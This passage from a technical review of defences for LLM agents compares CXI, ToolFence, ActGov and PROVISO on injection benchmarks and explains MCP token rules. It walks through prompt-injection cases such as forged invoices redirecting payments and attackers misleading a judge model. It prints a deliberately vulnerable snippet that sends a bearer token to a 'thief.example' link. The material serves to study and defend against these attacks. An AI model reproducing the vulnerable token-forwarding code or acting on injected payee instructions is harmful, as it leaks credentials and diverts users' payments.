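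The larger limitation is that what counts as an escape depends on how each test case's fixed policy classifies the fields. If the policy wrongly treated a dangerous field as harmless, the gate would admit the attack and the score would still be zero escapes. The live tests are therefore good evidence that the gate enforces its policy on the varied output of real models, but they can't show that the policy is right.

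### The cost in lost tasks

In the repository test, 134 of the 400 episodes ended before the agent could act, because the output was unreadable or its effect had no authorization. It is unclear how many of these ended because of CXI. Some unreadable outputs would have failed with any software that expects structured data, and some of the 61 unauthorized effects may have been bad patches that the validator correctly stopped. Running the same 400 episodes without CXI would have settled the question, but Santos-Grueiro reports no such run. For AgentDojo, the paper gives only the total of 199 safe completions across six conditions, so readers can't calculate how much the protection reduced task completion there either.

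One test suggests that the gate itself need not block much legitimate work. Santos-Grueiro ran 100 workflows with 270 steps in which data crossed the gate, and it didn't wrongly block any of them, but the policy already provided the releases these workflows used. In a real deployment, the likely problem is a task that needs a release nobody has written. If a user asks the agent to give a file the name suggested in a bug report, and no release exists for `new_name`, the gate blocks a reasonable request. The application can then ask the user to confirm the name, which makes it part of trusted state, but a user who has to do this often may start confirming without reading.

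Models can also become too cautious. In the test where four models wrote their own actions, each had 20 legitimate cases. GPT-OSS declined to make a call in every one of its cases, independently of the gate, so only 60 of the 80 legitimate actions took place.

Results from a similar system suggest that this kind of security can greatly reduce an agent's utility. On AgentDojo, Fan and colleagues reported complete security with their three strongest models, but the agents achieved only 38.1% to 46.4% utility. These figures aren't comparable with those for CXI because the setups differ.

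An action that passes the gate may still need further work. In an audit of 40 representative tasks, all 40 passed, but 11 needed human review, for example because the agent had not added a test for its repair.

Delay matters less for open-weight models, where preparing the mask took about 0.16 milliseconds per case. The hosted models needed separate requests for reading and writing, and a complete AgentDojo request took between 9.3 and 15.3 seconds. That wait may be acceptable for a payment but would be annoying in a conversation.

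### Routes around the gate

CXI's guarantee depends on several assumptions, and the first is that every side effect passes through the gate. An agent that has a shell and the password for the accounts system could send a payment request directly, and the gate would never check it. *Metis* (2026) points out that agents can often reach the same effect through tools with different checks, and that a gate should therefore report which routes it covers.

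*ZeroGate* (2026) lists routes that developers may overlook: retries, other credentials, direct calls to a service's programming library, programs started from a shell, and background workers. It also recommends a test in which the operator calls the protected service directly with the agent's credentials, then switches off the gate and checks whether any other worker can still perform the action. If either attempt succeeds, the gate doesn't protect that service. The simplest way to pass is to give the credentials to the gate instead of the agent.

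*CONTINUITY* (Zheng and Yang, 2026) describes a prototype that checks signed records from the user's original permission to the final action. When the researchers left open a direct route around the prototype in a test, the harmful effect took place, although every check on the normal route still worked.

The second assumption is that the host is trustworthy. The program that runs the gate also records which sources influenced each field. An attacker who controls this program can make it record that the log had no influence, and the gate will accept that record.

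### Permission that ends after the check

Even a gate that works as designed can allow an action just after its permission has ended. CXI checks the action against a snapshot of trusted data, uses up the capability and then runs the tool. If a manager withdraws an approval after the check, the lease alone does not stop the tool.

*Temporary Authority, Permanent Effects* (Santos-Grueiro, 2026) addresses this gap by moving the final check into the same indivisible operation as the change. In one experiment, coding agents had to publish a bug fix, but their permission to publish to production had been revoked beforehand without their knowledge. When the publishing service checked only whether the code was still the same version, it accepted all 12 unauthorized publications by agents based on GPT, Fable and Sonnet models. When it also checked the permission as it published, it accepted none.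 In 11 of 12 such cases, the agents then published to a test environment for which they had separate permission, so the refusal didn't waste their work.

A conditional write on INV-1042 would not detect a withdrawn approval, because withdrawing an approval doesn't change the invoice's version. The service has to check both the approval and the version.

### Mistakes in policies and validators

Writing a policy takes considerable work because it has to classify every field of every tool. Santos-Grueiro audited policies for 24 sinks with 149 fields, 85 of them protected. The first audit found 18 problems, nine of them serious. Some policies overlooked payloads that could cause effects, some let opaque text into too many places, and some accepted an approval written in ordinary language. Santos-Grueiro corrected them before the final results. Since the designer's own policies had these problems,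 other developers should expect to make mistakes too.

On 20 real MCP tools, software built by Fan and colleagues automatically assigned the right role to 87.1% of arguments and the right source to 77.4% of values. A company could use such software for a first draft, but a person would have to review the result because about one role in eight was wrong.

A correct policy can also become outdated. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (2026) describes schemas that no longer match what a tool does, and recommends checking the policy again whenever the tool changes. Some changes never appear in a schema. Suppose a deployment tool has an optional field, `environment`, and its server uses "staging" when the field is missing. If that default changes to "production", the same call has a much more serious effect. *SchemaCaps* (2026), a design for detecting tool updates that widen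 an agent's authority, treats such server defaults as unknown because the client can't see them. CXI's adapter has to include defaults when it calculates an effect, so the operator must have a reliable way to learn them or require the agent to fill in every field.

Validators are the remaining weak point. Suppose a company allows a typed release for `bank_account`, and its validator checks only the format and the check digits. If a thief sends a false invoice with their own account number, the number passes both checks and trusted code issues a release for it. The release names the right field, so the field check passes too, and the manifest then ties the payment securely to the thief's account.

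The wrong account can also enter after a correct approval. In an example from Zheng and Yang, a gateway approves a payment to `alias:merchant:9`, a short name for a merchant's account. The adapter that then converts the short name to an account number is faulty or compromised, and it inserts the attacker's number. If the system issues its permit after this step, the permit matches the attacker's payment exactly. CXI trusts its adapters, so it would have the same problem if one translated the name wrongly before the gate completed the manifest.

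Zheng and Yang's remedy is a signed statement from a separate directory that links the short name to the account. A verifier compares this statement with the adapter's output before issuing the permit. In 2,560 constructed attacks of 32 types, their full prototype allowed no harmful effects, while the best of the incomplete versions allowed them in 65.6% of cases. The tests did not involve a language model. The system relies on the directory being correct, so a false entry there would pass the check, like the clerk's entry in the supplier record.

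## ToolFence and ActGov: when a looked-up value may name a target

People often tell an agent where to find a target instead of writing it out. "Send the summary to my manager" requires the agent to look up an address, and "pay the account on the invoice" requires it to read an account number. Under Context-to-Execution Integrity, each such value needs a typed release that someone has prepared in advance. An application that accepts open-ended requests needs another way to decide which looked-up values its agent may use.

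Ameur, Mendes and Bouzefrane (2026), in *Intent-Conditioned Argument Mediation for Tool-Using LLM Agents*, tested two simple rules on 50 wrong actions and 50 legitimate ones, and both worked badly. The wrong values all came from trusted internal material. In one case, the user asks for a summary to go to a manager, and the agent picks the legal team's address from the company directory. A check that accepts any value from a trusted source let all 50 wrong actions through. A check that requires the target to appear word for word in the request stopped all 50, but also rejected 16 legitimate actions because the user had referred to a person or server by a short description. The tests are small and artificial, so they show what each rule can distinguish, not how often agents make such mistakes.

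### Two requests about one invoice

Suppose that a user gives the agent one of these instructions about INV-1042:

- **Invoice request:** "Pay the account on the invoice."
- **Register request:** "Pay our registered supplier for this invoice."

Both requests lead to a call such as `send_money(recipient, amount)`, and in both the amount comes from the invoice. Under the invoice request, the account can come from the invoice too. Under the register request, it must come from the company's supplier register, even if the invoice lists a different one. In each case the user has delegated the lookup, which means they have authorized a source for a field instead of a particular value.

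If a thief sends a forged invoice, an agent following the invoice request pays the thief as instructed. Paying the same account under the register request would break the agent's instructions, and the application can catch the error.

The permission has to cover the entry as well as the register. If the agent looks up Brandt Packaging instead of Brandt Paper, the account comes from the right register but the money goes to the wrong company.

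*Agenra* (2026), a language for writing agents' permissions, deals with this by having a rule fix the tool, its exact arguments and the field to read before the agent starts. The tool must also declare that field authoritative. In *Agenra*'s example, the line `resolve target: Lookup() -> destination` takes the recipient from the `destination` field of one designated lookup. For the register request, the rule would name the register, Brandt Paper's supplier number and the field `bank_account`. This is a strong check, but whoever writes the rule must already know the supplier. If the agent has to read the invoice to learn who sent it, the exact arguments aren't available yet.

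### How ToolFence checks the source of an argument

Li, Cao and Xiao (2026), in *ToolFence*, describe a system for requests that nobody has written rules for. It works as follows:

1. Before the agent reads any outside data, a language model called the compiler turns the user's request into a list of permissions, called capabilities. The compiler receives only the request and a reviewed description of the tools.
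2. Each capability names a tool, its effect, the number of times the agent may use it and the permitted source of each argument.
3. When the agent proposes a call, an ordinary program called the monitor looks for a matching capability and compares the arguments with it.
4. If everything matches, the monitor reserves one use and lets the call run. If an argument comes from the wrong source, the monitor refuses.
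5. If no capability covers the call, a separate model, the judge, decides whether to grant one. The agent then proposes the call again, and the monitor checks it in the usual way.

A capability can require an argument to equal a value from the request or from a trusted record that the application fixed before the start. It can also require the argument to come from the output of a named tool, or leave the choice to the agent if the argument is harmless. For the register request, the compiler should produce something like this:

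```text
send_money
  amount:    from get_invoice, field "amount"
  recipient: from get_supplier, field "bank_account"
  uses:      1
```

For the invoice request, the third line would name `get_invoice` instead. The thief's account on a forged invoice would then pass, but the capability above would block it.

The monitor's rule for looked-up values is looser than Agenra's. The value has to appear in output the named tool returned during the current session. If the agent has read the records of both Brandt Paper and Brandt Packaging, either account satisfies that rule. A capability can also list evidence that a call depends on. In one of Li and colleagues' examples, this stops an agent from using one order's verification code to complete another order. A supplier number could serve as that evidence here, provided the compiler includes it.

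#### What the judge model reads

Li and colleagues print the instructions for a judge that reviews one concrete call. Code first gives each argument a label:

- `user` means that the value occurs word for word in the user's request.
- `tool:<name>` means that the agent copied the value from that tool's output.
- `model` means that the value occurs in neither.

The judge may accept a `tool` label only if the user asked the agent to get that kind of value from that source, and it should refuse if it is unsure. In the instructions' example, a user who asks the agent to pay the bill in `bill-december-2023.txt` authorizes it to read the file and pay the stated amount to the stated recipient. By the same reasoning, the judge should accept an account labelled `tool:get_invoice` for the invoice request and refuse it for the register request.

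The judge that grants new capabilities reads the request and the proposed source of each argument, but not the values themselves. An attacker therefore can't mislead it with text hidden in an account name, but the judge also can't notice that a German supplier suddenly has a British account.

ToolFence stores the form of each granted capability and can reuse it in later sessions. This could be a problem for the two requests, because "recipient from `get_invoice`" is right for one and wrong for the other. Li and colleagues write that the system checks a reused capability against the new session's policies, but their experiments don't test this case separately.

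The prototype by Ameur and colleagues gives the `user` label to any fragment of the request, so `ager@company.com` passes if the user wrote `manager@company.com`. A program should compare complete addresses and account numbers instead. The program that Fan and colleagues use to trace arguments looks for exact matches first. If the origin of a sensitive argument remains ambiguous, the program assigns low trust without querying a model.

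### Results for ToolFence

Li and colleagues tested ToolFence with four agent models, all from 2025 or earlier, and used GPT-4.1-mini as compiler and judge. Besides AgentDojo and the Agent Security Bench, they used MCPTox, which hides instructions in tool descriptions, and AgentLAB, which spreads an attack over several records that the agent reads during a long task. The table gives the results for Qwen3-max, without and with ToolFence:

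| Benchmark | Successful attacks | Tasks completed under attack | Tasks completed without an attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| AgentDojo | 21.2% → 0.0% | 55.2% → 62.1% | 66.3% → 64.3% |
| Agent Security Bench | 40.2% → 4.2% | 46.3% → 48.4% | 71.5% → 67.2% |
| MCPTox | 38.1% → 6.1% | 43.4% → 56.2% | 67.2% → 65.4% |
| AgentLAB | 76.3% → 29.4% | 35.1% → 50.3% | 62.4% → 61.1% |

The other models gave similar results. No AgentDojo attack succeeded with any of the four models, including the 85 combinations of task and attack in which the attacker keeps the expected tool and changes only an argument, such as the recipient. On AgentLAB, 20.1% to 38.3% of attacks still succeeded. An attacker there can insert false options into the records so that a harmful step looks like a normal part of the job.

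On 200 AgentDojo cases, the protection raised the mean time per task from 6.3 to 10.3 seconds. The monitor adds fairly little time because it handles most calls without a model. CaMeL, a defence that turns the request into a program and runs it in a restricted interpreter, averaged 81.7 seconds on the same cases.

#### Removing one part at a time

Li and colleagues also switched off parts of ToolFence, using Llama 3.3 70B on the Agent Security Bench:

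| Version | Successful attacks | Tasks completed under attack | Judge calls per task | Running time |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| No defence | 45.4% | 40.1% | 0 | 1.0× |
| Full ToolFence | 5.1% | 44.3% | 0.9 | 1.8× |
| Without checks on arguments | 24.0% | 45.0% | 0.7 | 1.7× |
| Without new grants during the task | 4.8% | 35.8% | 0 | 1.5× |
| Judge reviews every call, with no fixed capabilities | 7.0% | 42.0% | 2.8 | 3.6× |

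The argument checks prevent many attacks. Grants during the task add almost no security, but without them the agent completes fewer tasks than it does with no defence, because the compiler often leaves out a legitimate step. More surprisingly, the last row shows that a judge without fixed capabilities did nearly as well against these attacks as the full system, and with 800 cases the gap between 7.0% and 5.1% might be chance. The clearer benefit of the fixed rules here is that they halve the running time.

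In a separate test, the researchers added conditions to a grant one by one and counted how many of 285 unauthorized calls got through:

| Conditions on the call | Unauthorized calls admitted |
|---|---|
| Right tool | 254 |
| Right tool and permitted sources | 231 |
| The same, at the right stage of the task | 118 |
| The same, with a use remaining | 5 |

Every version admitted all 227 legitimate calls. The source check stopped only 23 more calls, but this is weak evidence about its value in practice. The researchers chose how many wrong-stage and repeated calls to add to the data, and the proportions depend on those choices.

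The five remaining calls came from one task, in which the user's request presented the attacker's account as a "new landlord's". The account came from the user, so the check passed. Li and colleagues consider this a limit of any check based on origin. ToolFence would likewise accept the thief's account if the deceived clerk typed it into the instruction instead of into the supplier record.

### How ActGov uses recorded facts

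*ActGov* (Zhang, Peng and colleagues, 2026) uses the model differently. For every proposed call, ActGov fills in a list of facts, called records, and decides on the call by applying fixed rules to these records alone. Code fills in some records, such as whether the task permits the tool and whether an earlier permitted step read the document that the target comes from. A model fills in others by choosing from a short list. It classifies the origin of each argument, for example as "explicit user target", "trusted task artifact" or "untrusted injected content", and the role of a target, such as "payment payee". Further records combine these facts with "and", "or" and "not".

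Suppose a user asks the agent to download a price list from `brandt-paper.example`. One record shows whether the host in the download address matches the request or a trusted earlier result. A link to `brandt-paper.example/prices.pdf` matches the request, which supports the download. A link to `cheap-prices.example` that a stranger added in a comment matches neither. If the model also labelled that address as injected content, a fixed rule blocks the download.

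The two systems therefore use models for nearly opposite purposes:

| Decision | ToolFence | ActGov |
|---|---|---|
| Which tools the task needs | A model reads the request | Permissions that a model drafted before deployment |
| Where an argument came from | Code compares values | A model chooses a label |
| Whether that source is acceptable | Code applies the capability, or the judge considers a new one | Fixed rules |
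| Whether the call runs | Code | Code |

A model also drafts ActGov's rules, using descriptions of the tools, ordinary tasks and earlier attacks. A program called Z3 then searches for any combination of records that the rules allow but a list of security requirements forbids. If it finds one, the model revises the rules. An administrator reviews the final version before the application uses it. The search can prove that the rules meet the listed requirements, but it can't detect a false record. If the model labels the thief's account a "trusted task artifact", rules that passed the search may still let the payment through.

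#### The two requests under ActGov

For the invoice request, the model labels the recipient as a payment payee and classifies the origin of its account number. If it classifies the number as part of the task's context, and an earlier permitted step read the invoice, the rules can allow the payment. If it classifies the number as injected, the rules deny the payment. The right classification isn't obvious, because the user asked the agent to use the invoice, but the invoice came from outside the company.

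The register request is harder because ActGov's published list doesn't record which source the user named for each argument. If the agent takes the account from the invoice instead of the register, the model might still choose the same label, since the invoice is also part of the task, and the rules then would not block the payment. The permission for a task can state whether a target may come from tool results at all, but both requests need targets from tool results. A company could require payees to always come from its register, which would protect the register request but block the invoice request. That would be a sensible policy for many companies.

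### Results for ActGov

Zhang and colleagues used AgentDojo and AgentDyn, a benchmark in which agents often have to take legitimate targets from outside data. They developed the rules on half of each benchmark's attack cases, with GPT-5.5 as the drafting model and human review, and tested them on the other half. The table shows results without and with ActGov:

| Agent model | AgentDojo: successful attacks | AgentDojo: tasks completed under attack | AgentDyn: successful attacks | AgentDyn: tasks completed under attack |
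|---|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen3.6-flash | 6.9% → 0% | 85.7% → 67.3% | 4.6% → 0.4% | 65.0% → 58.6% |
| MiniMax-M2.5 | 3.1% → 0% | 85.7% → 70.0% | 3.6% → 0.4% | 62.5% → 54.6% |
| DeepSeek-v4-pro | 6.1% → 0% | 83.9% → 71.3% | 8.6% → 0.7% | 72.9% → 51.1% |
| GPT-4o mini | 3.6% → 0% | 69.0% → 60.6% | 11.1% → 0.7% | 41.4% → 34.3% |

On AgentDyn, the attack success rates with ActGov correspond to one or two successful attacks out of 280. The protection is clearly effective, but the paper's claim of "preserving task utility" is generous. With MiniMax-M2.5 on AgentDojo, ActGov prevented attacks in 3.1% of cases and reduced the task completion rate by 15.7 percentage points. Whether that is worthwhile depends on how much harm an attack could do. It may be worthwhile for an agent that makes payments, but probably not for one that manages a calendar.

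CaMeL completed no AgentDyn tasks with any of the four models. Looked-up targets may explain this, because a program written before the agent reads anything can't easily adapt to what the agent finds. But scores of zero in every setting could also result from a fault in how Zhang and colleagues adapted CaMeL to the benchmark.

The rules transferred poorly to new tasks. With DeepSeek-v4-pro and no attacks, the agent completed 60.0% of AgentDyn tasks under the rules developed for that benchmark, but 10.0% under those developed for AgentDojo. Completion on AgentDojo fell from 75.5% under its own rules to 22.4% under AgentDyn's. No attack succeeded in either transfer test, because the rules blocked most things they didn't cover. Many of the rules are very specific, such as an AgentDyn rule for reading a bank balance after a payment. A company with its own tools should therefore expect to develop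 its own rules.

Task completion also depended on which model drafted the rules. In a smaller trial without human review, the agent completed 53.3% of AgentDyn tasks under rules from DeepSeek-v4-pro when no attack was present. Under rules from two other models, it completed 28.3% and 31.7%. With all three sets of rules, at most 0.7% of attacks succeeded.

Zhang and colleagues claim that checking is fast but publish no timings. They also don't report how often the model chooses the right labels, and they don't remove parts of the system to measure what each contributes, so it is hard to tell how much of the security comes from the rules and how much from good labels.

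### Why the scores don't rank the systems

Both evaluations use AgentDojo, but their numbers aren't comparable because they used different agent models and attacks, and ActGov's test covers only half of the cases. Such differences can change scores substantially. With no attack, CaMeL completed between 32.1% and 48.4% of AgentDojo tasks in Li and colleagues' tests and between 18.4% and 30.6% in Zhang and colleagues'.

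A third system, *PROVISO* (Yan, Zhang and colleagues, 2026), is even less comparable. It uses a small neural network trained to choose between a proposed action and an alternative. The network's input separates the user's request from outside data, but the network learns from the outcomes of earlier cases instead of following a set rule about which source may supply a target. On AgentDojo, it chose between two complete attempts at each task, already made in a copy of the environment by two differently protected agents. ToolFence and ActGov don't have a second attempt to choose from. Attacks succeeded against PROVISO in 0.28% of cases, and the agent completed 85.4% of tasks under attack. PROVISO's choices gave a safe, completed task in 2,147 of 2,516 attacked cases, but always taking the first attempt would have done so in 2,066. Much of the score therefore comes from the attempts themselves.

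PROVISO's payment test is closer to the invoice problem. The user authorizes an invoice, but the notes and ledger entries the agent reads conflict with it in a quarter of cases. The network chose a correct payment in 88.5% of cases and an unsafe transfer in fewer than 0.4%. When the researchers stopped it from rereading the source material, correct payments fell to 78.5%, with the largest drop in the conflicting cases. A learned check can therefore compare a payment with its sources, but this network was trained on 2,048 similar cases, and few companies could supply that many for each tool.

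### A model's judgement or a fixed rule

The best argument for using a model is that something has to interpret the request. Comparing account numbers can't show that "our registered supplier" refers to the register and "the account on the invoice" doesn't. Two results support this argument: ToolFence completed fewer tasks without runtime grants, and ActGov performed poorly on unfamiliar tasks. Ameur and colleagues found a similar problem with a hand-written list of server names. In one test, their strict version executed only 14 of 30 legitimate requests because it blocked any server it couldn't identify from the list.

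But models make mistakes that a simple comparison would not. Yan and colleagues describe a case where a user asked for an extra Spotify payment after a price increase. Text in a past transaction told the agent to change the recipient of a regular payment to another account. TS-Guard, a model trained to detect unsafe tool calls, allowed the change. In another case, it blocked an email search the user had explicitly requested. Across the test, it missed 33 of 340 unsafe calls and blocked 20 of 367 safe ones. PROVISO missed one unsafe call and blocked five safe ones, but it had the advantage of training on other calls from the same benchmark.

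An attacker may also be able to influence the judge. ToolFence's judge for individual calls can receive excerpts of up to 400 characters from tool results, which an attacker may have written. The judge for new capabilities doesn't receive the values, but Li and colleagues report that it sometimes grants overly broad permissions when an attacker makes a harmful step look necessary. None of their attacks was designed to mislead the judge. The AgentLAB attacks, for instance, were fixed in advance and optimised against a different agent model. The low success rates may therefore underestimate how often an attacker who knows how ToolFence works would succeed.

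These results favour having a model interpret the request before it reads any outside data, and having code enforce that interpretation. For the register request, a model would decide once that the account must come from the register, and no later text on an invoice could change that. The difficult cases are those where the agent needs a new source halfway through. Mistakenly allowing it to read a file may do little harm, but if it is wrongly permitted to take a payee from an email, the whole payment can be lost, so the application should ask the user before giving that permission.

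Ameur and colleagues tried this with their server names. When the system asked the user about names it couldn't identify, it executed 28 of the 30 legitimate requests instead of 14, and still none of the 30 attacks. The researchers assumed that the user always answers correctly. For a payment, the question should show the account's source as well as its number. A manager is unlikely to recognise `GB29NWBK60161331926819` as wrong, but might well question an account labelled "from the invoice, not in the supplier register".

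## Access tokens and addresses found in tool results

A tool result can also contain a web address, such as a link to the next page of a list of invoices. If the client sends its access token to the wrong address, the damage can go far beyond a single payment. MCP uses bearer tokens, which give access to whoever presents them, so a thief who receives one can act as the user until it expires.

MCP's token rules come from OAuth, a family of standards that let an application act for a user without knowing the user's password. The MCP server holds the data, the client requests access to it, and an authorization server logs the user in and issues the token. Model Context Protocol's *Authorization* (2026) makes all of this optional and says that programs that run locally should take their credentials from their environment instead. For servers that do use tokens over HTTP, the July specification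 limits where the client may use its credentials.

### Naming the server a token is for

Suppose the accounts server has the address `https://accounts.example/mcp`. When the client asks for a token, it MUST include this parameter, defined in the standard RFC 8707:

```text
resource=https%3A%2F%2Faccounts.example%2Fmcp
```

The authorization server can then record that address in the token as its audience, the service that may accept it. Every MCP server MUST reject tokens meant for another service. A dishonest weather server therefore can't use the token it receives from the client to read the company's invoices.

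The client sends the parameter even if the authorization server ignores it. Model Context Protocol's *Authorization Security Considerations* (2026) notes that the binding works only if the authorization server supports it. Without that support, a compliant MCP server must find another way to verify that the token is for it or refuse the token.

A token's audience limits which servers should accept it, but not who may present it. If someone steals a token for the accounts server and presents it there, the audience check passes. The specification recommends short-lived tokens to limit the damage.

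### Checking who issued a login code

After the user logs in, the authorization server sends the browser back to the client with a code, which the client exchanges for a token. An attacker who runs one authorization server can try to obtain a code from another. This is a mix-up attack, and it could go as follows:

1. The user connects the client to a weather server whose authorization server, `login.weather.example`, belongs to the attacker.
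2. The attacker's server redirects the browser to the company's authorization server, `login.company.example`, with a request for access to the accounts server.
3. The user logs in, and the company's server sends the client a genuine code.
4. The client is still waiting for the weather login, so it sends the code to the attacker's server.
5. The attacker exchanges the code for a token to the accounts server.

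PKCE, an OAuth protection, requires the client to present a secret along with the code. It doesn't help here because the client sends the attacker that secret too, as the August 2026 draft of Model Context Protocol's *Security Best Practices* explains. The `resource` parameter doesn't help either, since the attacker can change it in step 2.

Another standard, RFC 9207, remedies this by having the authorization server add its own identifier, `iss`, to the response that carries the code. The client compares `iss` with the issuer it had recorded before opening the browser. In step 4, the client would find `login.company.example` instead of `login.weather.example` and stop.

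Since July, clients have been required (MUST) to make this comparison whenever a response contains `iss`, but authorization servers are only advised (SHOULD) to send it. If the company's server omits it, the attack can still succeed. The maintainers expect a future revision to require authorization servers to send it.

### Storing client credentials by issuer

Many client applications also have their own credentials, such as an ID and a secret, to identify themselves to an authorization server. Model Context Protocol's *Client Registration* (2026) requires clients to store these credentials under the identifier of the authorization server that issued them and never to use them with any other server.

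The MCP server specifies which authorization server the client should use, so someone who takes over the accounts server could specify an authorization server of their own. A client that had stored its secret under "accounts server" would send the secret there. A client that stores secrets by issuer has no entry for the new server, so it must register again. If a person set up the credentials by hand, the client should report an error instead.

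The rule doesn't apply to clients whose id is the web address of a public document describing them. They can use the same id everywhere, because any authorization server can look it up.

### Why a server may not pass a token on

The accounts server may itself need a service from the company's bank. The specification forbids the server from forwarding the client's token to the bank, so it has to get a separate token from the bank's authorization server.

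Forwarding would work only if the bank accepted tokens meant for the accounts server. Anyone who stole such a token could then use it directly with the bank and avoid any limits the accounts server imposes. The bank's logs could also show the wrong program as the source of the request, which would make fraud harder to investigate.

A server in the middle can still pose a risk when it uses separate tokens. Suppose the accounts server uses one fixed client id at the bank, and the bank has set a browser cookie recording that Alice approved that id. An attacker registers a new client with the accounts server and sends Alice a link that starts a login. The bank skips its consent page because of the cookie, and the accounts server sends the resulting authorization code to the attacker's client. To prevent this, the accounts server must ask Alice to approve each new client before it contacts the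 bank.

### A next page on another host

None of these rules stops a client from sending a properly issued token to an address it found in a result. Suppose `list_invoices` returns a few invoices at a time, with a link to the next page. The accounts server also collects invoices from suppliers' portals, and a thief who controls one portal has supplied the link:

```json
{
  "invoices": ["INV-1041", "INV-1042"],
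  "next_page_url": "https://accounts.example.thief.example/invoices?page=2"
}
```

The link passes `"format": "uri"` because it is a well-formed address. The client then follows it, using the Python library `requests`:

```python
page = requests.get(result["next_page_url"],
                    headers={"Authorization": "Bearer " + token})
```

The host belongs to `thief.example`, so the thief now has the token. The thief's server can return a plausible second page so that nobody notices. HTTPS doesn't prevent this, because the thief can get a certificate for that host. A signature on the result would also be valid, since the accounts server did send the link.

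The client could choose which token to send based on the host in the link, so that only `accounts.example` receives the accounts token. This prevents the leak, but a malicious weather server could then return a link to `accounts.example`, and the client would make a request there with the user's permissions.

In the repaired version, the client's own configuration determines the host and the credential. The result supplies only a page marker, in a field named `next_page`:

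```python
ACCOUNTS_URL = "https://accounts.example/invoices"

def next_page(result):
    return requests.get(ACCOUNTS_URL,
                        params={"page": result["next_page"]},
                        headers={"Authorization": "Bearer " + ACCOUNTS_TOKEN},
                        allow_redirects=False)
```

The library encodes special characters in `params`, so the marker can't change the rest of the address. Joining the strings directly would be unsafe. If a program adds `@thief.example/` to `https://accounts.example`, the resulting address leads to `thief.example`, because everything between `https://` and the `@` counts as a user name.

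The Model Context Protocol (MCP) uses cursors to page through its own lists. The response to `tools/list` has a `nextCursor` field, whose value the client sends back to the same server as `cursor`. A tool such as `list_invoices` can also take a cursor as an ordinary argument.

Some existing services return only complete links. The client can then parse the link and require its scheme, host and port to exactly match the configured ones. Checking only the start of the link would let the thief's link through, because it also begins with `https://accounts.example`. Even with an exact match, the path still comes from the result, so a link to another part of the accounts system would pass.

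A page marker can pass schema validation and still skip the page that lists a disputed invoice. It can also point to invoices the user isn't allowed to read, so the server must check permissions for every page.

The MCP guidance doesn't directly cover this example. *Security Best Practices* has detailed rules for addresses, but most concern those that a client fetches during an OAuth login. One rule requires clients to validate all URLs from MCP servers, but the thief's link would pass the checks it lists, such as rejecting characters with a special meaning in a shell.

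### Redirects and resource links

A request to the right host can still end up elsewhere if that host redirects it. Some HTTP libraries remove the `Authorization` header when a redirect leads to another host, but they may still forward a key in a custom header. The function above doesn't follow redirects. A client that needs to follow them should check each new address before sending the credential again.

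Following a bad link can do harm even without a token. On many cloud machines, `http://169.254.169.254/` leads to an internal service that supplies the machine's credentials. For OAuth URLs, the Model Context Protocol draft recommends blocking private and reserved network addresses, including after a redirect. It also warns that a host name can lead to a harmless machine when it is checked and an internal one when the request is sent. The same precautions make sense for links in tool results.

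Mohiuddin's individual draft on MCP security collects public reports of servers that fetched pages for an agent from any address they received. One report concerns a tool that controls a web browser. If the browser is already logged in to the user's accounts, it attaches the credentials itself, so an attacker doesn't need the client to mishandle a token.

A tool can also return a resource link, such as `file:///project/src/main.rs`. The safest approach is for the client to request the content from the server that returned the link, using `resources/read` and that server's token. If the client opened a `file:` link itself, it might read a private file from the user's disk. The client can't validate the link against the server's resource list, because linked resources don't have to appear there.

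Sometimes the user wants a document from whatever address a result contains. ToolFence permits delegated lookups like this. The client can then fetch the document without sending a credential, after checking that the address isn't internal.

### When a handle is only a name

The `basket_id` in the shopping basket example described earlier is a handle, which Model Context Protocol calls "a name, not a capability" on servers that authenticate their users. For the permission check on each call, *Security Best Practices* recommends storing every handle together with its owner:

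```python
def add_item(token, basket_id, sku):
    user = verify(token)
    basket = BASKETS.get((user, basket_id))
    if basket is None:
        raise ToolError("unknown or expired basket")
    basket.append(sku)
```

`verify` checks the token, including its audience, and returns the user's ID. If Bob copies Alice's `basket_id` from a shared transcript, the server looks for that ID among Bob's baskets and finds nothing. He gets the same error as for a basket that doesn't exist, so he can't use the tool to find out which basket IDs are real. For shared baskets, the server needs a list of permitted users instead.

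This also stops the reverse attack, in which malicious text gets Alice's agent to use Bob's basket. If Alice has two baskets, it doesn't stop the agent from using the wrong one, because she has permission to use both.

On a server without authentication, the handle works like a bearer token, and the specification's example, `bsk_a1b2c3`, would be too easy to guess. If the six characters after the prefix are hexadecimal digits, there are about 16.8 million possible values. With 10,000 active baskets, an attacker would find one after about 1,700 guesses on average. The specification suggests a UUIDv4, which has 122 random bits. At 1,000 guesses a second, finding one of 10,000 baskets would then take around 10²² years.

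A handle also needs to expire, because randomness doesn't protect it once it has leaked. The specification gives the example of a basket that expires after 24 hours of inactivity. But an attacker with a leaked handle could keep the basket from ever expiring by opening it once a day, so a fixed maximum age would be safer.

### Does the new specification shift security to developers?

In *MCP's new spec turns a planted prompt into a stolen credential* (VentureBeat, 7 September), Kale (2026) claims that the July specification moves enforcement from the protocol to developers and to endpoints, the machines on which agents run. Earlier versions let a server identify a session by an id in an HTTP header. The July version instead uses handles that appear in the conversation, and Kale considers any handle that an attacker plants or reads through prompt injection a valid credential.

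Kale is right that the state has moved. The July revision removed sessions, and servers that need to remember something between calls now create handles. The release announcement (Model Context Protocol, 2026) presents the handles' visibility as an advantage, because the model can pass a handle from one tool to another. That visibility also means handles can end up in transcripts, logs and support tickets.

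The claim that the protocol itself once enforced ownership checks is much weaker. *Migrate Sessions to Stateless Requests with MCP 2026-07-28* (Vaswani, 2026) notes that the previous version let each server decide whether to issue session ids. According to PolicyLayer, a security vendor, the earlier guidance already told developers to tie session ids to users and verify both on every request. The Agentic AI Foundation says developers understood sessions differently, so two conversations could end up sharing state. A developer who skipped the ownership check was therefore exposed before July too.

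A stolen handle works as a credential on a server that has no authentication, or that looks up the handle without checking the user. It doesn't work on a server that follows the Model Context Protocol's guidance. The protocol forbids servers to treat possession of a handle as authentication, but tying the handle to a user is only a SHOULD.

For tokens, the July revision added requirements that library authors can implement once for many applications, such as checking `iss` and storing credentials by issuer. Kale lists audience-bound tokens among the issues the new version raises, but the June 2025 edition had already made the `resource` parameter mandatory (Model Context Protocol, 2025).

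Kale also argues that network security tools can't detect these attacks. That is true for servers on the user's own computer, whose traffic never crosses the network. With a remote server, a gateway that decrypts the traffic can read the handle in the tool call. But the gateway usually has no record of who owns the basket, so the server should check ownership.

This part of the argument closely follows Pik (2026), *New MCP Spec Opens Three New Attack Surfaces. Security, Get Ready*, written two months before the final specification. Pik works for Backslash, which sells endpoint security and so benefits if companies believe that only endpoint software can help. But Pik's first recommendation, to make sure the server ties each handle to a user, requires no endpoint product.

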